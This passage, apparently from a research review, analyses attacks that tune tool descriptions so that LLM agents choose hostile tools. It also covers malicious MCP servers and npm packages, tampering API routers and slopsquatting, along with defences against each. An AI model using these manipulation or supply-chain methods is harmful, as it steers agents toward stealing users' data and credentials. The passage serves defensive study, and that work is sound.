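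| *D* | The descriptions of the other available tools |
| *M* | The model's choice, given the request and all the descriptions |
| 1( ) | 1 if the model chooses the hostile tool, 0 if it doesn't |
| E | The average over all the phrasings, which is the selection rate |
| *d*₀ | An honest tool's description |
| Δ, *η* | The difference in meaning between the two descriptions, and the most the attacker allows |

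If 20 people ask for the weather in different words and the model calls the hostile tool for 16 of them, the selection rate is 80%. Without the limit *η*, the winning description might be a blunt command or a wild boast that a reader would notice. The formula doesn't depend on what the tool does, so the same description gets the same score for a working service as for one that steals keys.

The attacker can't measure this average directly, because other people send the requests. All three attacks estimate it from sample requests, but they differ in what else the attacker can see.

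### ToolHijacker and the two stages

The attacker in ToolHijacker, by Shi and colleagues, knows which task to target but can't see the catalogue, the retriever, the model or the users' requests, and can't send test requests to the agent. The attacker therefore builds a practice system with its own model and tools, and hopes that the target agent will also choose a tool whose description wins there.

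Each description has one part for the retriever, which resembles the way users phrase the task, and another that pushes the model to pick the tool. Shi and colleagues tested the parts separately on one task with GPT-4o:

| Description | Reached the shortlist | Chosen |
|---|---|---|
| Both parts | 100% | 99% |
| Retriever part only | 100% | 5% |
| Model part only | 65% | 63% |

When the tool's description contained only the part written for the model, GPT-4o picked the tool almost every time it was on the shortlist, but the tool didn't make the shortlist for about a third of the requests.

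The main test used two catalogues, one of 199 tools and one of 9,650. For each catalogue, the team chose seven tasks, wrote 100 versions of each request and had the retriever shortlist five tools per request. GPT-4o chose the hostile tool for 96.4% of requests with the small catalogue and 85.1% with the large one. With the large catalogue, the hostile tool was shortlisted for 95.1% of requests, so GPT-4o must have chosen it about 89% of the time when it was shortlisted.

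Simple handwritten commands did much worse. The best won 32% of GPT-4o's choices, mainly because text that only gives orders has little in common with a request about, say, the weather, so a retriever is less likely to select it. Retrievers therefore offer some accidental protection against crude attacks.

All eight models in the study are long out of date. The 700 requests per catalogue also tested only seven hostile descriptions, so the results are better evidence about different request phrasings than about different tools.

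### ToolTweak and five equal tools

In ToolTweak, Sneh and colleagues treat the attacker as a company selling a tool through a marketplace. The company can read the names and descriptions of rival tools, see a sample of users' requests and track how often agents choose its tool. It can change its tool's name and description but not its input format.

The target model sees five tools directly, with no retriever. All five can do the same job, such as forecasting the weather or checking an email address. An attacking model proposes a new name and description for one tool, the target model answers 100 requests, and the attacking model uses the outcome to try again. The final result is the best version from ten rounds.

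Before the attack, a tool received about 20% of the requests on average, as expected with five equal tools. The attack raised this to as high as 81%, which leaves the other four tools with an average of 4.75% each, or less if the model sometimes fails to call any tool. The rivals therefore lose about three quarters of their requests, although their products haven't changed.

That figure is for DeepSeek Chat, the most susceptible of six models. GPT-OSS 20B reached 73.6%, and Llama 3.1 8B reached 34%. Each rate is the best of several attempts on the same requests, so the rates on new requests would probably be somewhat lower.

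Sneh and colleagues also tried adding the same sales pitch to every target tool's description. This beat ToolTweak's repeated revision on five of the six models and reached 89.5% with Grok 3 Mini. An attacker who knew neither the requests nor the rival tools, and saw only usage figures, still reached about 60% with DeepSeek.

Even a meaningless detail in a tool's name can affect whether a model chooses it. When two otherwise identical tools had names ending in 1 and 2, Qwen 2.5 7B chose the one ending in 1 in 72.6% of trials. Sneh and colleagues suspect that the model treats the number as a ranking.

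### TSA and models the attacker never tested

TSA's attacker has no access to the target agent either. Dai and colleagues tuned the descriptions against Llama 3.3 70B and then tested them on other models. In the main tests, the agent had 10 or 20 tools, including the malicious tool and a legitimate one for the same task. Some of the tools came from real MCP servers.

The paper reports an average success rate of 83.23%. This seems to cover only Llama 3.3, since it matches the average of that model's six results. On four models that the attacker had not used for tuning, the average with ten tools was slightly lower, at 81.91%. The highest rate was 92.13%, for GPT-5. GPT-5 is more than a year old, but Qwen3.8, a model from 2026, also chose the hostile tool for about 75% of requests.

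Dai and colleagues ran older attacks on the same four models:

| Attack | Average selection rate on unseen models |
|---|---|
| TSA | 81.9% |
| ToolHijacker | 67.7% |
| AMA, which also revises descriptions repeatedly | 64.7% |
| A tag that marks the description as important | 47.6% |
| GAPMA, which rewrites descriptions by fixed advertising rules | 39.3% |

The tag and GAPMA follow fixed rules and don't learn from the model's choices, which probably explains why they do worse. But such measurements can be unstable. Dai and colleagues repeated part of the original GAPMA experiment with ten requests per tool. With a GPT model, the success rate was 0% in the original paper and 90% in the rerun for a tool that tells the time, and 0% and 100% for a news tool.

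The sample for TSA is also small. Most of its percentages are consistent with a total of 141 test requests, which would give each result a margin of error of roughly plus or minus four to seven points. The average is more reliable than the highest of the eight results, 92.13% for GPT-5.

TSA's descriptions mostly escaped the detectors and human readers that the team tested.

### Why the percentages are hard to compare

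| | ToolHijacker | ToolTweak | TSA |
|---|---|---|---|
| What the attacker knows | The task | Rival tools, sample requests and usage figures | The task and publicly listed tools |
| Tools the model sees | 5, from a catalogue of 199 or 9,650 | 5 | 10 or 20 |
| Suitable honest tools | 4 or 5 per task in the small catalogue | 4 | 1 in the main tests |
| Models | 8, including GPT-4o and Claude 3.5 Sonnet | 6, including DeepSeek Chat and Gemini 2.5 Flash Lite | 5, including GPT-5 and Qwen3.8 |
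| Selection rate of the hostile tool | 70% to 100% | 34% to 82% | 73% to 92% |

How often a model with no preference would choose the hostile tool depends on the number of suitable honest tools. The rate is 20% in ToolTweak, where there are four equally suitable honest tools, and about 50% in TSA's main tests, where there is one.

One can adjust for this by comparing the hostile tool's share with the average share of a suitable rival. If *s* is the hostile tool's selection rate and *n* the number of suitable rivals, the ratio is

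*r* = *s* / ((1 − *s*)/*n*) = *ns* / (1 − *s*)

For ToolTweak on DeepSeek, *r* is 4 × 0.816 / 0.184, so the model chose the hostile tool about 18 times as often as each rival. On Llama 3.1, *r* is only about 2. For TSA on Llama 3.3 with ten tools, the selection rate was 88.65% against one honest tool, so *r* is about 8. By this measure, ToolTweak's best result is stronger than TSA's, although its percentage is lower. The calculation is rough because it assumes that every request the attacker lost went to a suitable rival.

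With three suitable honest tools, TSA's selection rate fell from 88.65% to 75.88%, but the same ratio rose slightly, to about 9. Extra honest tools take some requests from the attacker because the model has more tools to choose from, but they don't make it better at recognising the hostile one. The attacker can also add tools. With three hostile tools and one honest one, the attacker's total share was 95%, though a model with no preference would have given the attacker 75%.

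### Rewriting the descriptions

Since biased wording attracts the model, an obvious defence is to reword the descriptions before the model chooses. Sneh and colleagues had each target model paraphrase all the descriptions in neutral language, removing opinions but keeping the essential facts. They then let the attacker revise its text against this defence:

| Model | No attack | ToolTweak | With paraphrasing | After the attacker adapts |
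|---|---|---|---|---|
| DeepSeek Chat | 20.1% | 81.6% | 48.6% | 59.7% |
| GPT-OSS 20B | 18.9% | 73.6% | 63.3% | 67.9% |
| Grok 3 Mini | 19.9% | 50.7% | 32.7% | 44.8% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash Lite | 18.8% | 48.6% | 30.1% | 37.5% |
| Qwen 2.5 7B | 19.9% | 45.9% | 34.3% | 46.7% |
| Llama 3.1 8B | 19.8% | 33.9% | 27.2% | 34.4% |

On DeepSeek, the attack increased the tool's share by 61.5 percentage points. Paraphrasing removed 33 of those points, and an attacker who adapted to the defence regained 11. On Qwen and Llama, the adapting attacker regained everything that paraphrasing had removed. The defence worked much better against the ready-made sales pitch, whose selection rate fell to between 20% and 38%.

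Paraphrasing a tool's description can't remove all the bias, partly because it leaves the tool's name unchanged. It also doesn't check whether claims are true. A neutral rewording of "replies in half the time of other services" still contains the claim that the service is faster.

The defence requires an extra model call for each description, although an agent could store the new text until the publisher changes the original. Sneh and colleagues don't report the added time or expense, or test whether the agent still completes its tasks as well. The rewriting also changes honest descriptions, and it doesn't always make the choice fairer. It brought the model's choices closer to an even split in 88% of cases with DeepSeek but only 42% with Llama 3.1.

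*TRUSTDESC* (2026) takes a more radical approach and replaces the publisher's description with one that reflects the tool's actual code. In one test, an agent chose between tools from 12 MCP servers and versions of them with worse code. When Claude Sonnet 4.5 wrote the descriptions, the agent chose the less secure version 32.5% of the time, compared with 50% expected by chance. Descriptions by gpt-oss-120b emphasised features instead, so the result depends on which model writes them.

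This needs access to the code, which limits its use against counterfeit APIs. An MCP server's code may show only that it sends data to a certain address. Software on the attacker's machine then determines what happens to the data.

### Filtering by perplexity

Perplexity measures how surprising a text is to a language model. For a description of *N* tokens, *w*₁ to *w*<sub>*N*</sub>, it is

PPL = exp( −(1/*N*) Σ log *p*(*w*ᵢ | *w*₁, …, *w*ᵢ₋₁) )

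where *p* is the probability that the model gives to each token after reading the ones before it. If every token had a probability of 1/20, the perplexity would be 20. Gibberish has a high perplexity, so a filter can reject text above a chosen threshold. This can catch attacks that consist of odd strings of characters.

A filter that rejects descriptions with high perplexity is unlikely to catch fluent sales language. Sneh and colleagues used GPT-2 to score the descriptions from their attacks on DeepSeek and Llama 3.1. On average, these had lower perplexity than the honest descriptions, and the two ranges overlapped almost completely. A filter that rejected unusually low perplexity instead would also reject honest descriptions that were clearly written.

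Shi and colleagues found much the same for ToolHijacker. One filter, which checks a few tokens at a time, caught two of the 14 hostile descriptions tested in the large catalogue and wrongly flagged 2.99% of the honest tools, or nearly 290 of 9,650. Calculating perplexity takes little compute, but somebody would have to review the wrongly flagged tools or lose them.

Length may help a little in detecting manipulated descriptions. ToolTweak's descriptions were typically much longer than honest ones, and Sneh and colleagues suggest that a filter could combine length with perplexity, though they haven't built one. Such a filter might soon stop working, since ToolHijacker's descriptions were no longer than ordinary ones.

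Asking a language model to look for manipulation worked better against ToolHijacker. Shi and colleagues say their descriptions contain no obvious instructions, and two models trained to ignore commands in outside text still chose the hostile tool in 87% to nearly 100% of cases. But Dai and colleagues found strong commands in the descriptions ToolHijacker produced for them, and a simple detector based on a language model flagged 85% of these descriptions on one benchmark. The results may differ because the descriptions were different, or because spotting a command is a different task from resisting one. A prompt injection detector that Dai and colleagues tried flagged every honest description as well, perhaps because saying what a tool does can resemble an instruction to use it.

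### Getting onto the list, and rivals that aren't equal

A selection rate of 90% applies only to agents that already have access to the hostile tool. If one in 200 users had installed it, the attacker would get 0.5% × 90%, or 0.45%, of all requests for the task. Dai and colleagues acknowledge that the attack fails if nobody installs the tool. Attackers therefore need a way to get it installed, such as publishing a fake server or package in a vendor's name.

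Unlike the other two, ToolHijacker requires its tool to get past the retriever, but it still assumes that the catalogue accepts the tool. Dai and colleagues published a harmless version of their server on an MCP platform and then simulated a user connecting to it. They report a success rate of 100%, which shows that they could publish the server, but not that strangers would have installed it.

The experiments also assume that the honest tools do the job equally well. In practice, the attack may be harder than in the experiments if an honest tool has a real advantage, such as a useful function that the hostile tool lacks, or easier if there is no honest tool for the exact request, as in the SolanaApis theft.

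Fame could also protect some vendors. Claude Code chose Stripe for nearly every payment task, and a clever description from an unknown company might not change that. None of the three papers reports separate results for attacks against famous brands. The results are probably most relevant to tasks with many little-known providers, such as looking up the location of an internet address.

### What the model knows about the publisher

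A person choosing between two email services would want to know who runs them. A tool's name, description and input format don't establish this, and an attacker can copy all three. Anbiaee, Dadkhah and Ghorbani (2026), in *When Tool Names Are Not Identities*, tested how much each of them matters. They gave an agent one honest MCP server, which could fetch and store a dataset, and one hostile server. For each combination, the agent received ten versions of the request five times each. The table shows how often it chose the hostile tool:

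| Hostile tool | GPT-5.4 | Claude Sonnet 5 | Gemini 2.5 Pro | Qwen3.7 Max | DeepSeek V3 |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Copied description, different name | 0% | 0% | 0% | 0% | 22% |
| Description claims approval or security, different name | 4% | 0% | 42% | 20% | 50% |
| Copied name and description | 100% | 6% | 84% | 100% | 100% |
| Copied name and description, unsuitable inputs | 0% | 0% | 0% | 0% | 0% |

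(In the first three rows, the hostile tool accepted the inputs that the task required.)

Copying another tool's description rarely got a model to choose the hostile tool. An unverified claim, such as that a company had approved the tool, had more effect on four of the five models. When Anbiaee and colleagues repeated that test with five different tool names, GPT-5.4 chose the hostile tool 25% of the time instead of 4%. The models usually avoided tools that couldn't accept the right inputs, and none chose such a tool when both its name and description were copied. But when the tool had the copied name and its description claimed approval or security, DeepSeek V3 chose it 56% of the time and Qwen3.7 Max 18%.

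In the third row, the two tools had the same name and description, so the wording can't explain why three models chose the hostile one every time. A model with no preference would have split its choices about evenly. The order of the tools, or the way the client handles duplicate names, may have determined the choice. Some model providers don't allow two tools with the same name. When the attacking model in ToolTweak tried to copy a rival's name, the provider's API rejected the duplicate.

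Claude Sonnet 5 instead asked the user which tool to use in 94% of the trials with a copied name and description. This is safer than guessing, but it helps only if the user can tell the two servers apart.

Yeon, Chaudhary and Singh (2025), in *Quantitative Certification of Agentic Tool Selection*, tested credibility labels by letting software add tools with unverified labels, such as "official" or "enterprise", to a catalogue of 300 tools. One fake booking tool marked as official won nine out of ten rounds against a real one. With Llama 3.1 8B, one round of added tools cut the highest plausible rate of suitable choices from 81% to 50%. The paper's headline figure of 20% is lower because it requires a suitable choice in all ten rounds.

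The labels were only part of the cause. When Yeon and colleagues removed them, along with the copied input formats and lookalike names, the ten-round figure rose only to 33%. Guaranteeing a suitable tool on the shortlist raised it to 43%, so the model often failed to choose a suitable tool even when one was listed. None of five other defences, including a perplexity filter, raised the figure above 30%. The four models in the main tests had only 4 to 14 billion parameters, and larger ones may be less susceptible.

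These studies show that models respond to claims about a publisher, but they don't test the effect of verifying those claims. Anbiaee and colleagues conclude that agents need a verified provider identity for each tool. That is a reasonable inference, but they didn't test whether models choose better with one. A program could also enforce the identity by refusing any tool from the wrong publisher before the model sees it.

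*Agents' Overreliance on Unreliable Tools* (2026) is the closest test of a trust signal, though it covers what tools return after the model has called them. It found that reliability labels on web search results made agents somewhat less likely to accept false information. Sometimes an agent questioned a result in its reasoning but still passed it on to the user without a warning. A label may therefore help a model notice a problem without making the model act on it.

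ProbeID tries to identify a tool by its behaviour. It sends each candidate inputs for which it already has trusted replies, and uses the answers to choose among the candidates. This could expose a tool that copies an honest tool's description but works differently. It would have more trouble with a counterfeit API that forwards each request to the real vendor and keeps a copy of the data for the attacker, because the replies would be correct.

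## Fake servers and packages published in a vendor's name

In September 2025, an npm package called postmark-mcp sent its users' email through Postmark but also sent a copy of every message to its publisher. Two related cases followed in 2026. One was a malicious copy of an MCP server for the Oura Ring, which tracks sleep, and the other was PromptMink, a campaign that planted malicious packages in crypto projects. Only the PromptMink case includes evidence that a model chose the attackers' software.

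### postmark-mcp and its extra recipient

Infosecurity Magazine's *Malicious AI Agent Server Reportedly Steals Emails* says that Jabal Torres, a technical marketing designer at Postmark, created the company's own MCP server. The code was on GitHub, but Postmark says it had not published the server on npm before the incident. Somebody with the npm account "phanpak" copied the code and published it there under the same name, so a developer who looked for Postmark's server on npm could find only the copy.

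Koi, the security company that discovered the attack, says the first 15 versions worked properly. Version 1.0.16 added one line of code that put an address at giftshop[.]club in the blind-copy (BCC) field of every outgoing email.

Suppose the shop owner's assistant had used this version to tell the customer that order 12345 had shipped. The model would have supplied the customer's address, the subject and the text, and the server would have added the hidden recipient before passing the request to Postmark. Postmark would have delivered both copies and returned "OK". Asking the shop owner to approve the call would not have helped, because the client shows the model's inputs, and the server would have added the extra address afterwards.

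A shipping notice is of little use to a thief, but companies also email invoices and password resets. Anyone who receives a copy of a password reset may be able to use the link before the customer does.

Koi attributes the package's success to trust. The publisher appeared to use his real name, had legitimate projects on GitHub, and released a series of harmless versions first. Koi also suggests that the package was harmless for months, but ThaiCERT's *Researchers Discover First Malicious MCP Server in Rogue Postmark-MCP Package* (2025), a notice from Thailand's computer emergency team, dates its release to 15 September and the malicious version to 17 September. The Hacker News (2025) gives the same date for the malicious version. If these dates are right, the publisher had two days to build a reputation, so the familiar name and working code probably mattered more.

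### How many people installed it

The only measured figure is Koi's count of about 1,500 downloads a week. Koi guessed that 20% of the downloads were in active use, which would mean 300 organisations. It also guessed that each organisation sent 10 to 50 emails a day, so the attacker would have received 3,000 to 15,000 a day. If only 2% of the downloads were in use, the same calculation would give 30 organisations and 300 to 1,500 emails a day.

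The 1,500 figure counts downloads rather than users, and one user can download a package several times. Automated systems download packages too. Some of the downloads may also have been of harmless versions. Neither Koi nor Postmark names a victim.

The malicious version was probably available for little more than a week. OSV's *MAL-2025-47604* (2025), published on 26 September, confirms that version 1.0.16 sent out email data. The publisher deleted the package from npm after Koi contacted him. This stopped new installations, but installed copies kept sending email to the attacker until somebody removed them.

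None of these reports shows that a model chose the package. Koi says that developers recommended it to their teams, which suggests that people chose it. A model became involved later, when an assistant called the installed tool to send an email. If the user had no other email tool, the assistant had no alternative, so the high selection rates from laboratory experiments have little bearing on this case.

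### The cloned Oura server

In February 2026, the security company Straiker reported a hostile copy of an MCP server that gives assistants access to sleep and other health data from the Oura Ring. According to Straiker's *SmartLoader Clones Oura Ring MCP to Deploy Supply Chain Attack* (2026), Tomek Korbak, an engineer at OpenAI, had published the original on GitHub about 11 months earlier. The original was not an Oura product, and Oura seems to have made no public statement.

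Straiker describes several months of preparation. About three months before the report, one GitHub account made a harmless copy of Korbak's project, and four others copied that copy. A month later, another account published a version with malware and listed some of these accounts as contributors, which made the project look like the work of a small community.

Straiker says the accounts were fake and that one person or group ran them all. Its evidence is that they were new, behaved similarly and made changes at around the same time. This is suggestive, but real developers who copied a popular project in the same few weeks could look much the same. Straiker's "smoking gun" is that the hostile version left Korbak out of the contributor list. That fits an attempt to hide the project's origin, but copying the files without their history would also remove his name. The malware is much stronger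 evidence against the account that published it than against the accounts with harmless copies.

The hostile version also appeared on MCP Market, a public catalogue of MCP servers, alongside legitimate ones. Its source code matched the original, so reading the code would not have revealed the attack. The malware was in a separate download that contained a program disguised as a text file, resource.txt. This program installed StealC, which collects browser passwords, login sessions, crypto wallets and API credentials. The malware also set itself to run again under names that resembled a common audio driver.

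Straiker says the attack exposed thousands of developers and users, but it gives no count of downloads or infections. It also lists health data among the attackers' targets, although its technical analysis doesn't show the malware collecting any. A stolen Oura credential could give access to that data, but there is no evidence that the attackers used one.

Straiker says victims could find the server through GitHub, a registry or a recommendation. A coding agent could have found it in the first two ways as easily as a person, but Straiker gives no example of an agent doing so.

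### Chatbots that recommended similar fakes

*AgentBaiting* (2026), a report by the security company Island, provides better evidence about models. It describes a larger operation that used the same two malware programs, SmartLoader and StealC. Island found about 7,600 malicious GitHub repositories. More than 800 of them posed as MCP servers or skills for AI agents, and these had more than 600 listings in public catalogues. Island couldn't tell whether the attackers had submitted the listings or the catalogues had collected them automatically.

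One of the fakes was advertised as an MCP server with 263 tools for connecting agents to Databricks, a data platform. The Windows download contained no MCP server, only three files that ran the malware. The damage was done as soon as somebody ran the download, so unlike with postmark-mcp, no model had to choose it from among the installed tools.

Island's researchers asked Gemini for a link to a free Walmart MCP server, and its first recommendation was one of the malicious repositories. ChatGPT answered the same request with three options and called the malicious one the best place to start. Neither chatbot had received a link to the repository.

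The researchers also asked Claude Code to find a free skill for writing cinematic prompts and explain how to install it. It recommended a harmless skill but offered a malicious one as an alternative, then repeated the attacker's instructions to click past any security warning. In other runs, Claude Code noticed the files were suspicious and refused to recommend the repository.

These tests show that a chatbot can lead a user to a counterfeit without having seen a link to it. They don't show how often this happens, because Island reports only a few examples and knew which fakes existed when it wrote the requests. In each example, a person still had to download and run the file.

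Island counted more than 14 million downloads from about 200 of the repositories. That figure covers the whole operation, including many projects unrelated to AI, and it is unclear how many downloads led to an infection.

### PromptMink's two layers of packages

The security company ReversingLabs described PromptMink in April 2026. Pezo (2026), in *Claude adds malware to crypto agent*, explains that the attackers used two kinds of npm package. A bait package did something useful for crypto developers and contained no malicious code. It depended on a second package that stole secrets, and npm installs dependencies automatically.

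The best-known example looked like this:

```
openpaw-graveyard             a crypto trading agent
  └─ @solana-launchpad/sdk    the bait, which has working functions
       └─ @validate-sdk/v2    the payload, which steals secrets
```

An SDK (software development kit) is ready-made code for using a service or platform. The bait's name includes "Solana", and another bait package used pump.fun's name. Both packages exploited well-known names, but Pezo doesn't say they copied an official product.

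The bait also hid its one harmful dependency, disguised as a tool for checking data, among many popular ones. A developer or agent that read only the bait's code would have found nothing wrong, and most of the dependency list would have looked familiar.

The split also made the campaign hard to stop. ReversingLabs first flagged an earlier payload, @hash-validator/v2, on 25 September 2025, and npm removed it on 7 October. The attackers published @validate-sdk/v2 the same day, with the same code and version number. They then released a new version of the bait that pointed to the new payload, so the bait kept its name and whatever reputation it had built up.

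At first, the payload looked for files that often contain API keys and other secrets. Later versions also gave the attackers remote access to the machine and copied the source code of whole projects. Over seven months, ReversingLabs counted 60 packages and more than 300 versions.

Pezo attributes the campaign to Famous Chollima, a North Korean group known for fake job interviews that trick developers into running malware. Part of his evidence is weak, since many criminals target crypto developers and many programmers use Vercel, the hosting service the attackers used. The campaign's similarity to others attributed to North Korea is more persuasive. The Hacker News (2026) also reports the attribution but credits it to ReversingLabs, so it isn't independent confirmation.

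### Did the attackers write for coding agents?

Pezo says that coding agents "might have been" the real targets. His main evidence is that the packages' README files, the introductions shown on their pages, contained boasts about how well each package did its job. He also points to the large number of packages. Elsewhere, the same post says that the packages deceived agents more successfully than people, but it gives no numbers for either.

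Boastful documentation can attract people as well as models. One README still contained language-model output offering to obfuscate the README as well. This is good evidence that the attackers used a model to write the package, but it doesn't show that they wrote it to attract models.

Pezo also says that the attackers moved the harmful code into compiled files, which a language model can't easily read. But he says they did this only to avoid detection, after earlier versions had been caught and removed. The attackers may therefore have been mainly concerned with security scanners.

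ReversingLabs found two projects that used the bait. In January 2026, a bot called Zora wrote on Moltbook, a discussion site for AI agents, that it had created a crypto token. Zora later explained that @solana-launchpad/sdk had a function it needed. This suggests that the bot chose the package because it fitted the task, as in the SolanaApis theft. But this is the bot's own account after the fact, and its owner may have suggested the package.

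The second case is the trading agent openpaw-graveyard. On 28 February 2026, its developer saved a change that added the bait package. The project's history lists Claude Opus as co-author, so Claude probably helped write the change. The history doesn't show who thought of the package. Claude may have found it in a search, or the developer may have asked for it by name.

The conversation between Claude and the developer would show whether the package's name first appeared in the user's request, a search result or the model's answer, as the published ChatGPT conversation did for the SolanaApis theft. The headline that Claude added malware is slightly misleading, because Claude helped to add the bait package, and npm installed the malware with it. Pezo doesn't report any money stolen from either project.

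Before publishing a package, attackers can also run a coding agent themselves to see whether it picks the package. Pezo sees this as the main difference from tricking human developers. ToolTweak used the same kind of trial and error to improve tool descriptions, but there is no direct evidence that the PromptMink attackers used it.

### What a hostile tool can do

The harm depends on where the attacker's software runs:

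| Attacker's position | What the attacker can read | What the attacker can change |
|---|---|---|
| A counterfeit API on a remote server | Each request, including any key in it | The replies |
| A package or MCP server on the user's machine | Requests, and any files the agent can open | Replies, files and stored data |
| A router between the agent and the model | The conversation with the model, including any keys in it | The model's answers and the commands it gives the agent |

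*MalTool* (Hu, Jia and colleagues, 2026) studies the second position and lists 13 kinds of harmful behaviour in three groups: stealing information, tampering with data or programs, and making the system slow or unusable. A tool normally receives only the inputs the model gives it, not the rest of the conversation. But it runs with the agent's permissions, so a weather tool that receives only the name of a city may still be able to open the file that holds the user's API keys.

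A tool can also put false records into an agent's memory or the documents it consults. The agent could then keep giving wrong answers based on those records after the user removes the tool.

Hu and colleagues then tested how easily a language model could write such tools. One program asked a coding model for a tool with a given harmful behaviour. Another checked that the tool worked and differed enough from earlier ones, and the process repeated until a tool passed both checks. The average cost per working tool ranged from $0.013 with GPT-4o to $0.033 with Claude Opus 4.6. At the higher price, 1,300 tools, 100 for each behaviour, would cost about $43.

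The team also added harmful code to 5,727 real tools from public catalogues. Hu and colleagues report that six detection systems, including the malware scanner VirusTotal and Cisco's scanner for MCP servers, missed many malicious tools in both sets and flagged many harmless ones. Some of those flags may have been correct, because the supposedly harmless tools came from catalogues that have also listed malware, including MCP Market, where Straiker found the Oura clone.

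*MalTool* gives three conditions for a successful attack: a user installs the tool, the model selects it, and its code does something harmful. Some real attacks didn't need the second condition, because they worked without a model calling a tool. These include PromptMink, the Oura clone, Island's fake Databricks server and mcp-server-postgres, an npm package that posed as the official MCP server for the PostgreSQL database. OSV's *MAL-2026-5481* (2026) says that the npm package ran a script during installation and sent out the computer's name. A defence that only helps the model choose among installed tools would come too late for such packages.

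### Routers that alter the model's answers

A router sits between the agent and the model, so a hostile one can cause harm even if the model chooses the right API. If the model tells a coding agent to install the genuine Postmark package, the router could change the package name, and the agent would install the attacker's package instead. *The Proxy Knows Too Much* (2026) points out that a coding agent runs such commands with the developer's permissions.

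In April 2026, Liu and colleagues reported a test of 428 routers. They bought access to 28 from online shops, including the Chinese marketplaces Taobao and Xianyu, and collected 400 free ones from public communities. Nine routers (2.1%), one paid and eight free, added malicious code to responses. Two routers used triggers to avoid detection, so a simple test could miss them.

The team also planted credentials for Amazon's cloud service that would reveal any attempt to use them. Seventeen routers used them, and one router took cryptocurrency from a wallet after receiving its private key. Stealing credentials may therefore be more common than adding code, and it is harder to notice because the answers can stay correct.

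An honest operator can also expose its customers if it passes their requests through another operator's insecure service. Liu and colleagues set up weakly protected decoys to see whether this happened. The decoys handled 2 billion tokens of traffic and exposed 99 credentials across 440 Codex sessions. In 401 of those sessions, the agent could already act without asking for approval, so an attacker who changed its instructions might not have needed anyone to approve its actions.

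A later study found no such attacks. Wu, Zhao and colleagues (2026), in *What the Middleman Delivers*, tested 20 routers that offered GPT-6 Astra and Claude Opus 5, and found no confirmed malicious additions in 3,332 responses. This doesn't contradict the earlier result. If 2.1% of routers added malicious code, the chance that a random sample of 20 would include none is

(1 − 9/428)²⁰ ≈ 0.65

or about 65%. The large number of responses doesn't change this much, because they came from only 20 services. The samples also differed. Wu and colleagues chose services with an English website that accepted a credit card or PayPal, which ruled out many of the kind sold on Taobao. They sent fixed, harmless requests without running any commands, so they could have missed attacks that wait for a real agent or a valuable credential.

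The tests did reveal other problems. In the first round, four routers returned tool calls although the request had disabled them, but none did so in the second round. Five routers reported 4,200 to 60,000 more input tokens than the official API did for the same requests, and at least one charged for the extra tokens. The extra tokens may be hidden instructions that the router added to the request, or the router may count tokens differently.

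Seven of the ten cheaper routers also gave answers that differed from the official model's, compared with two of the ten that charged the same or more. A cheaper substitute model could explain the different answers, but so could changed settings, and the difference between the two groups could be due to chance (*p* = 0.07).

People choose a router to save money, to pay in a convenient way or to reach models that aren't available in their region, according to Wu and colleagues. *Where Is the Cost of Third-Party API Routers in Agentic Software Development?* (2026) adds that developers use routers to manage keys and to switch to another model when one fails. Because people rather than models make this choice, the router studies show what an intermediary can do but are not evidence of API SEO. A chatbot could still influence the choice. Wu and colleagues found some of their 20 routers by asking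 ChatGPT, Claude, Gemini and Grok for recommendations, and an attacker could try to get a hostile router into such recommendations.

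## Package names and web addresses that models invent

In slopsquatting, an attacker registers a name that models tend to invent and waits. The attacker doesn't have to promote a counterfeit, as the people behind SolanaApis did, or copy a name that users already trust, as the publisher of postmark-mcp did. Willison (2025) credits the word to Seth Larson, a security developer at the Python Software Foundation.

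Suppose the shop owner's coding agent needs a package to check postal addresses, and it writes an install command for one that nobody has published. npm returns an error, the agent tries something else, and no harm is done. If an attacker had already registered the name, the same command would have installed the attacker's code.

### Why the same name has to come back

An attacker has to register a name before a victim's model writes it. How often a model invents names therefore matters less than how often it invents the same one:

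expected installs = *N* × P(model invents a name) × P(it is this name, given that it invents one) × P(user installs it)

*N* is the number of requests for the task. Suppose developers make 10,000 requests and the model invents a package in 5% of its answers, or 500 times. If 60% of those answers contain the same name, whoever registers it could reach 300 developers. If all 500 names are different, each registration reaches one developer.

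The standard study of the problem is *We Have a Package for You!* (2024), by Spracklen, Wijewickrama and colleagues. They had 16 models write 576,000 Python and JavaScript code samples and checked whether the packages existed. According to Socket's summary, commercial models invented 5.2% of the packages they recommended and open models invented 21.7%. GPT-4 Turbo had the lowest rate, 3.59%, and two CodeLlama models invented more than a third of theirs.

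Spracklen and colleagues also took 500 prompts that had produced an invented name and ran each ten more times. The models repeated 43% of the names in all ten runs and never repeated 39%. An attacker could find the names that recur by running the same prompts several times. But of the more than 205,000 different names in the study, 81% were each invented by only one model.

### Package names in 2026

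*The Range Shrinks, the Threat Remains* gave the same prompts to five newer models in April 2026 and collected 199,840 answers. It counted a name as invented only if the live registry had no such package when the model wrote it. It also tried to exclude correct import statements, because a Python package's import name can differ from its install name. For example, programs load the package opencv-python with "import cv2".

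| Model | Invented share of package mentions | Answers with an invented package | Answers without usable code |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 3.6% | 2.3% | 1.3% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 4.1% | 2.8% | 18.8% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 4.8% | 3.4% | 8.1% |
| DeepSeek V3.2 | 4.8% | 2.7% | 2.0% |
| GPT-5.4-mini | 5.0% | 2.2% | 31.5% |

GPT-5.4-mini has the highest rate per mention but the lowest per answer, mainly because it so often returned no code.

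It is unclear whether commercial models have improved since 2024. These rates are slightly lower than those of 2024, but earlier versions of the paper, which used the package lists from the 2024 study, gave 4.6% to 6.1%. The paper also says that the gap between open and commercial models has disappeared, but it tested only one open model, DeepSeek V3.2. Smaller open models still do much worse. *Evaluating Inference-Time Defenses Against Package Hallucination in LLM-Generated Code* (2026) tested eight models, including some with fewer than two billion parameters, and found that they invented 24.7% of the Python packages they named.

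All five models in the April test invented the same 104 names. These are under 5% of the 2,282 invented names but 42% of all mentions of invented names. More than half of the 104 are one character away from a real package's name, so the problem partly overlaps with typosquatting. Even these shared names are rare in general programming, each appearing 26 times on average, or about once in 7,700 answers.

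An invented name may also belong to an existing package, so checking that the package exists doesn't show that it is safe to use. Raj and Sahu (2026), in *Names Can Hurt*, used software to flag suspicious packages in code from two Llama models. Of the 179 flags, 90 were for names already on PyPI, Python's main registry, which they describe as squats or low-quality lookalikes. However, 46 of those 90 flags were for pil and faiss, which are correct import names for well-known packages, so the true share of squats is probably well below half.

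### Agents that look names up

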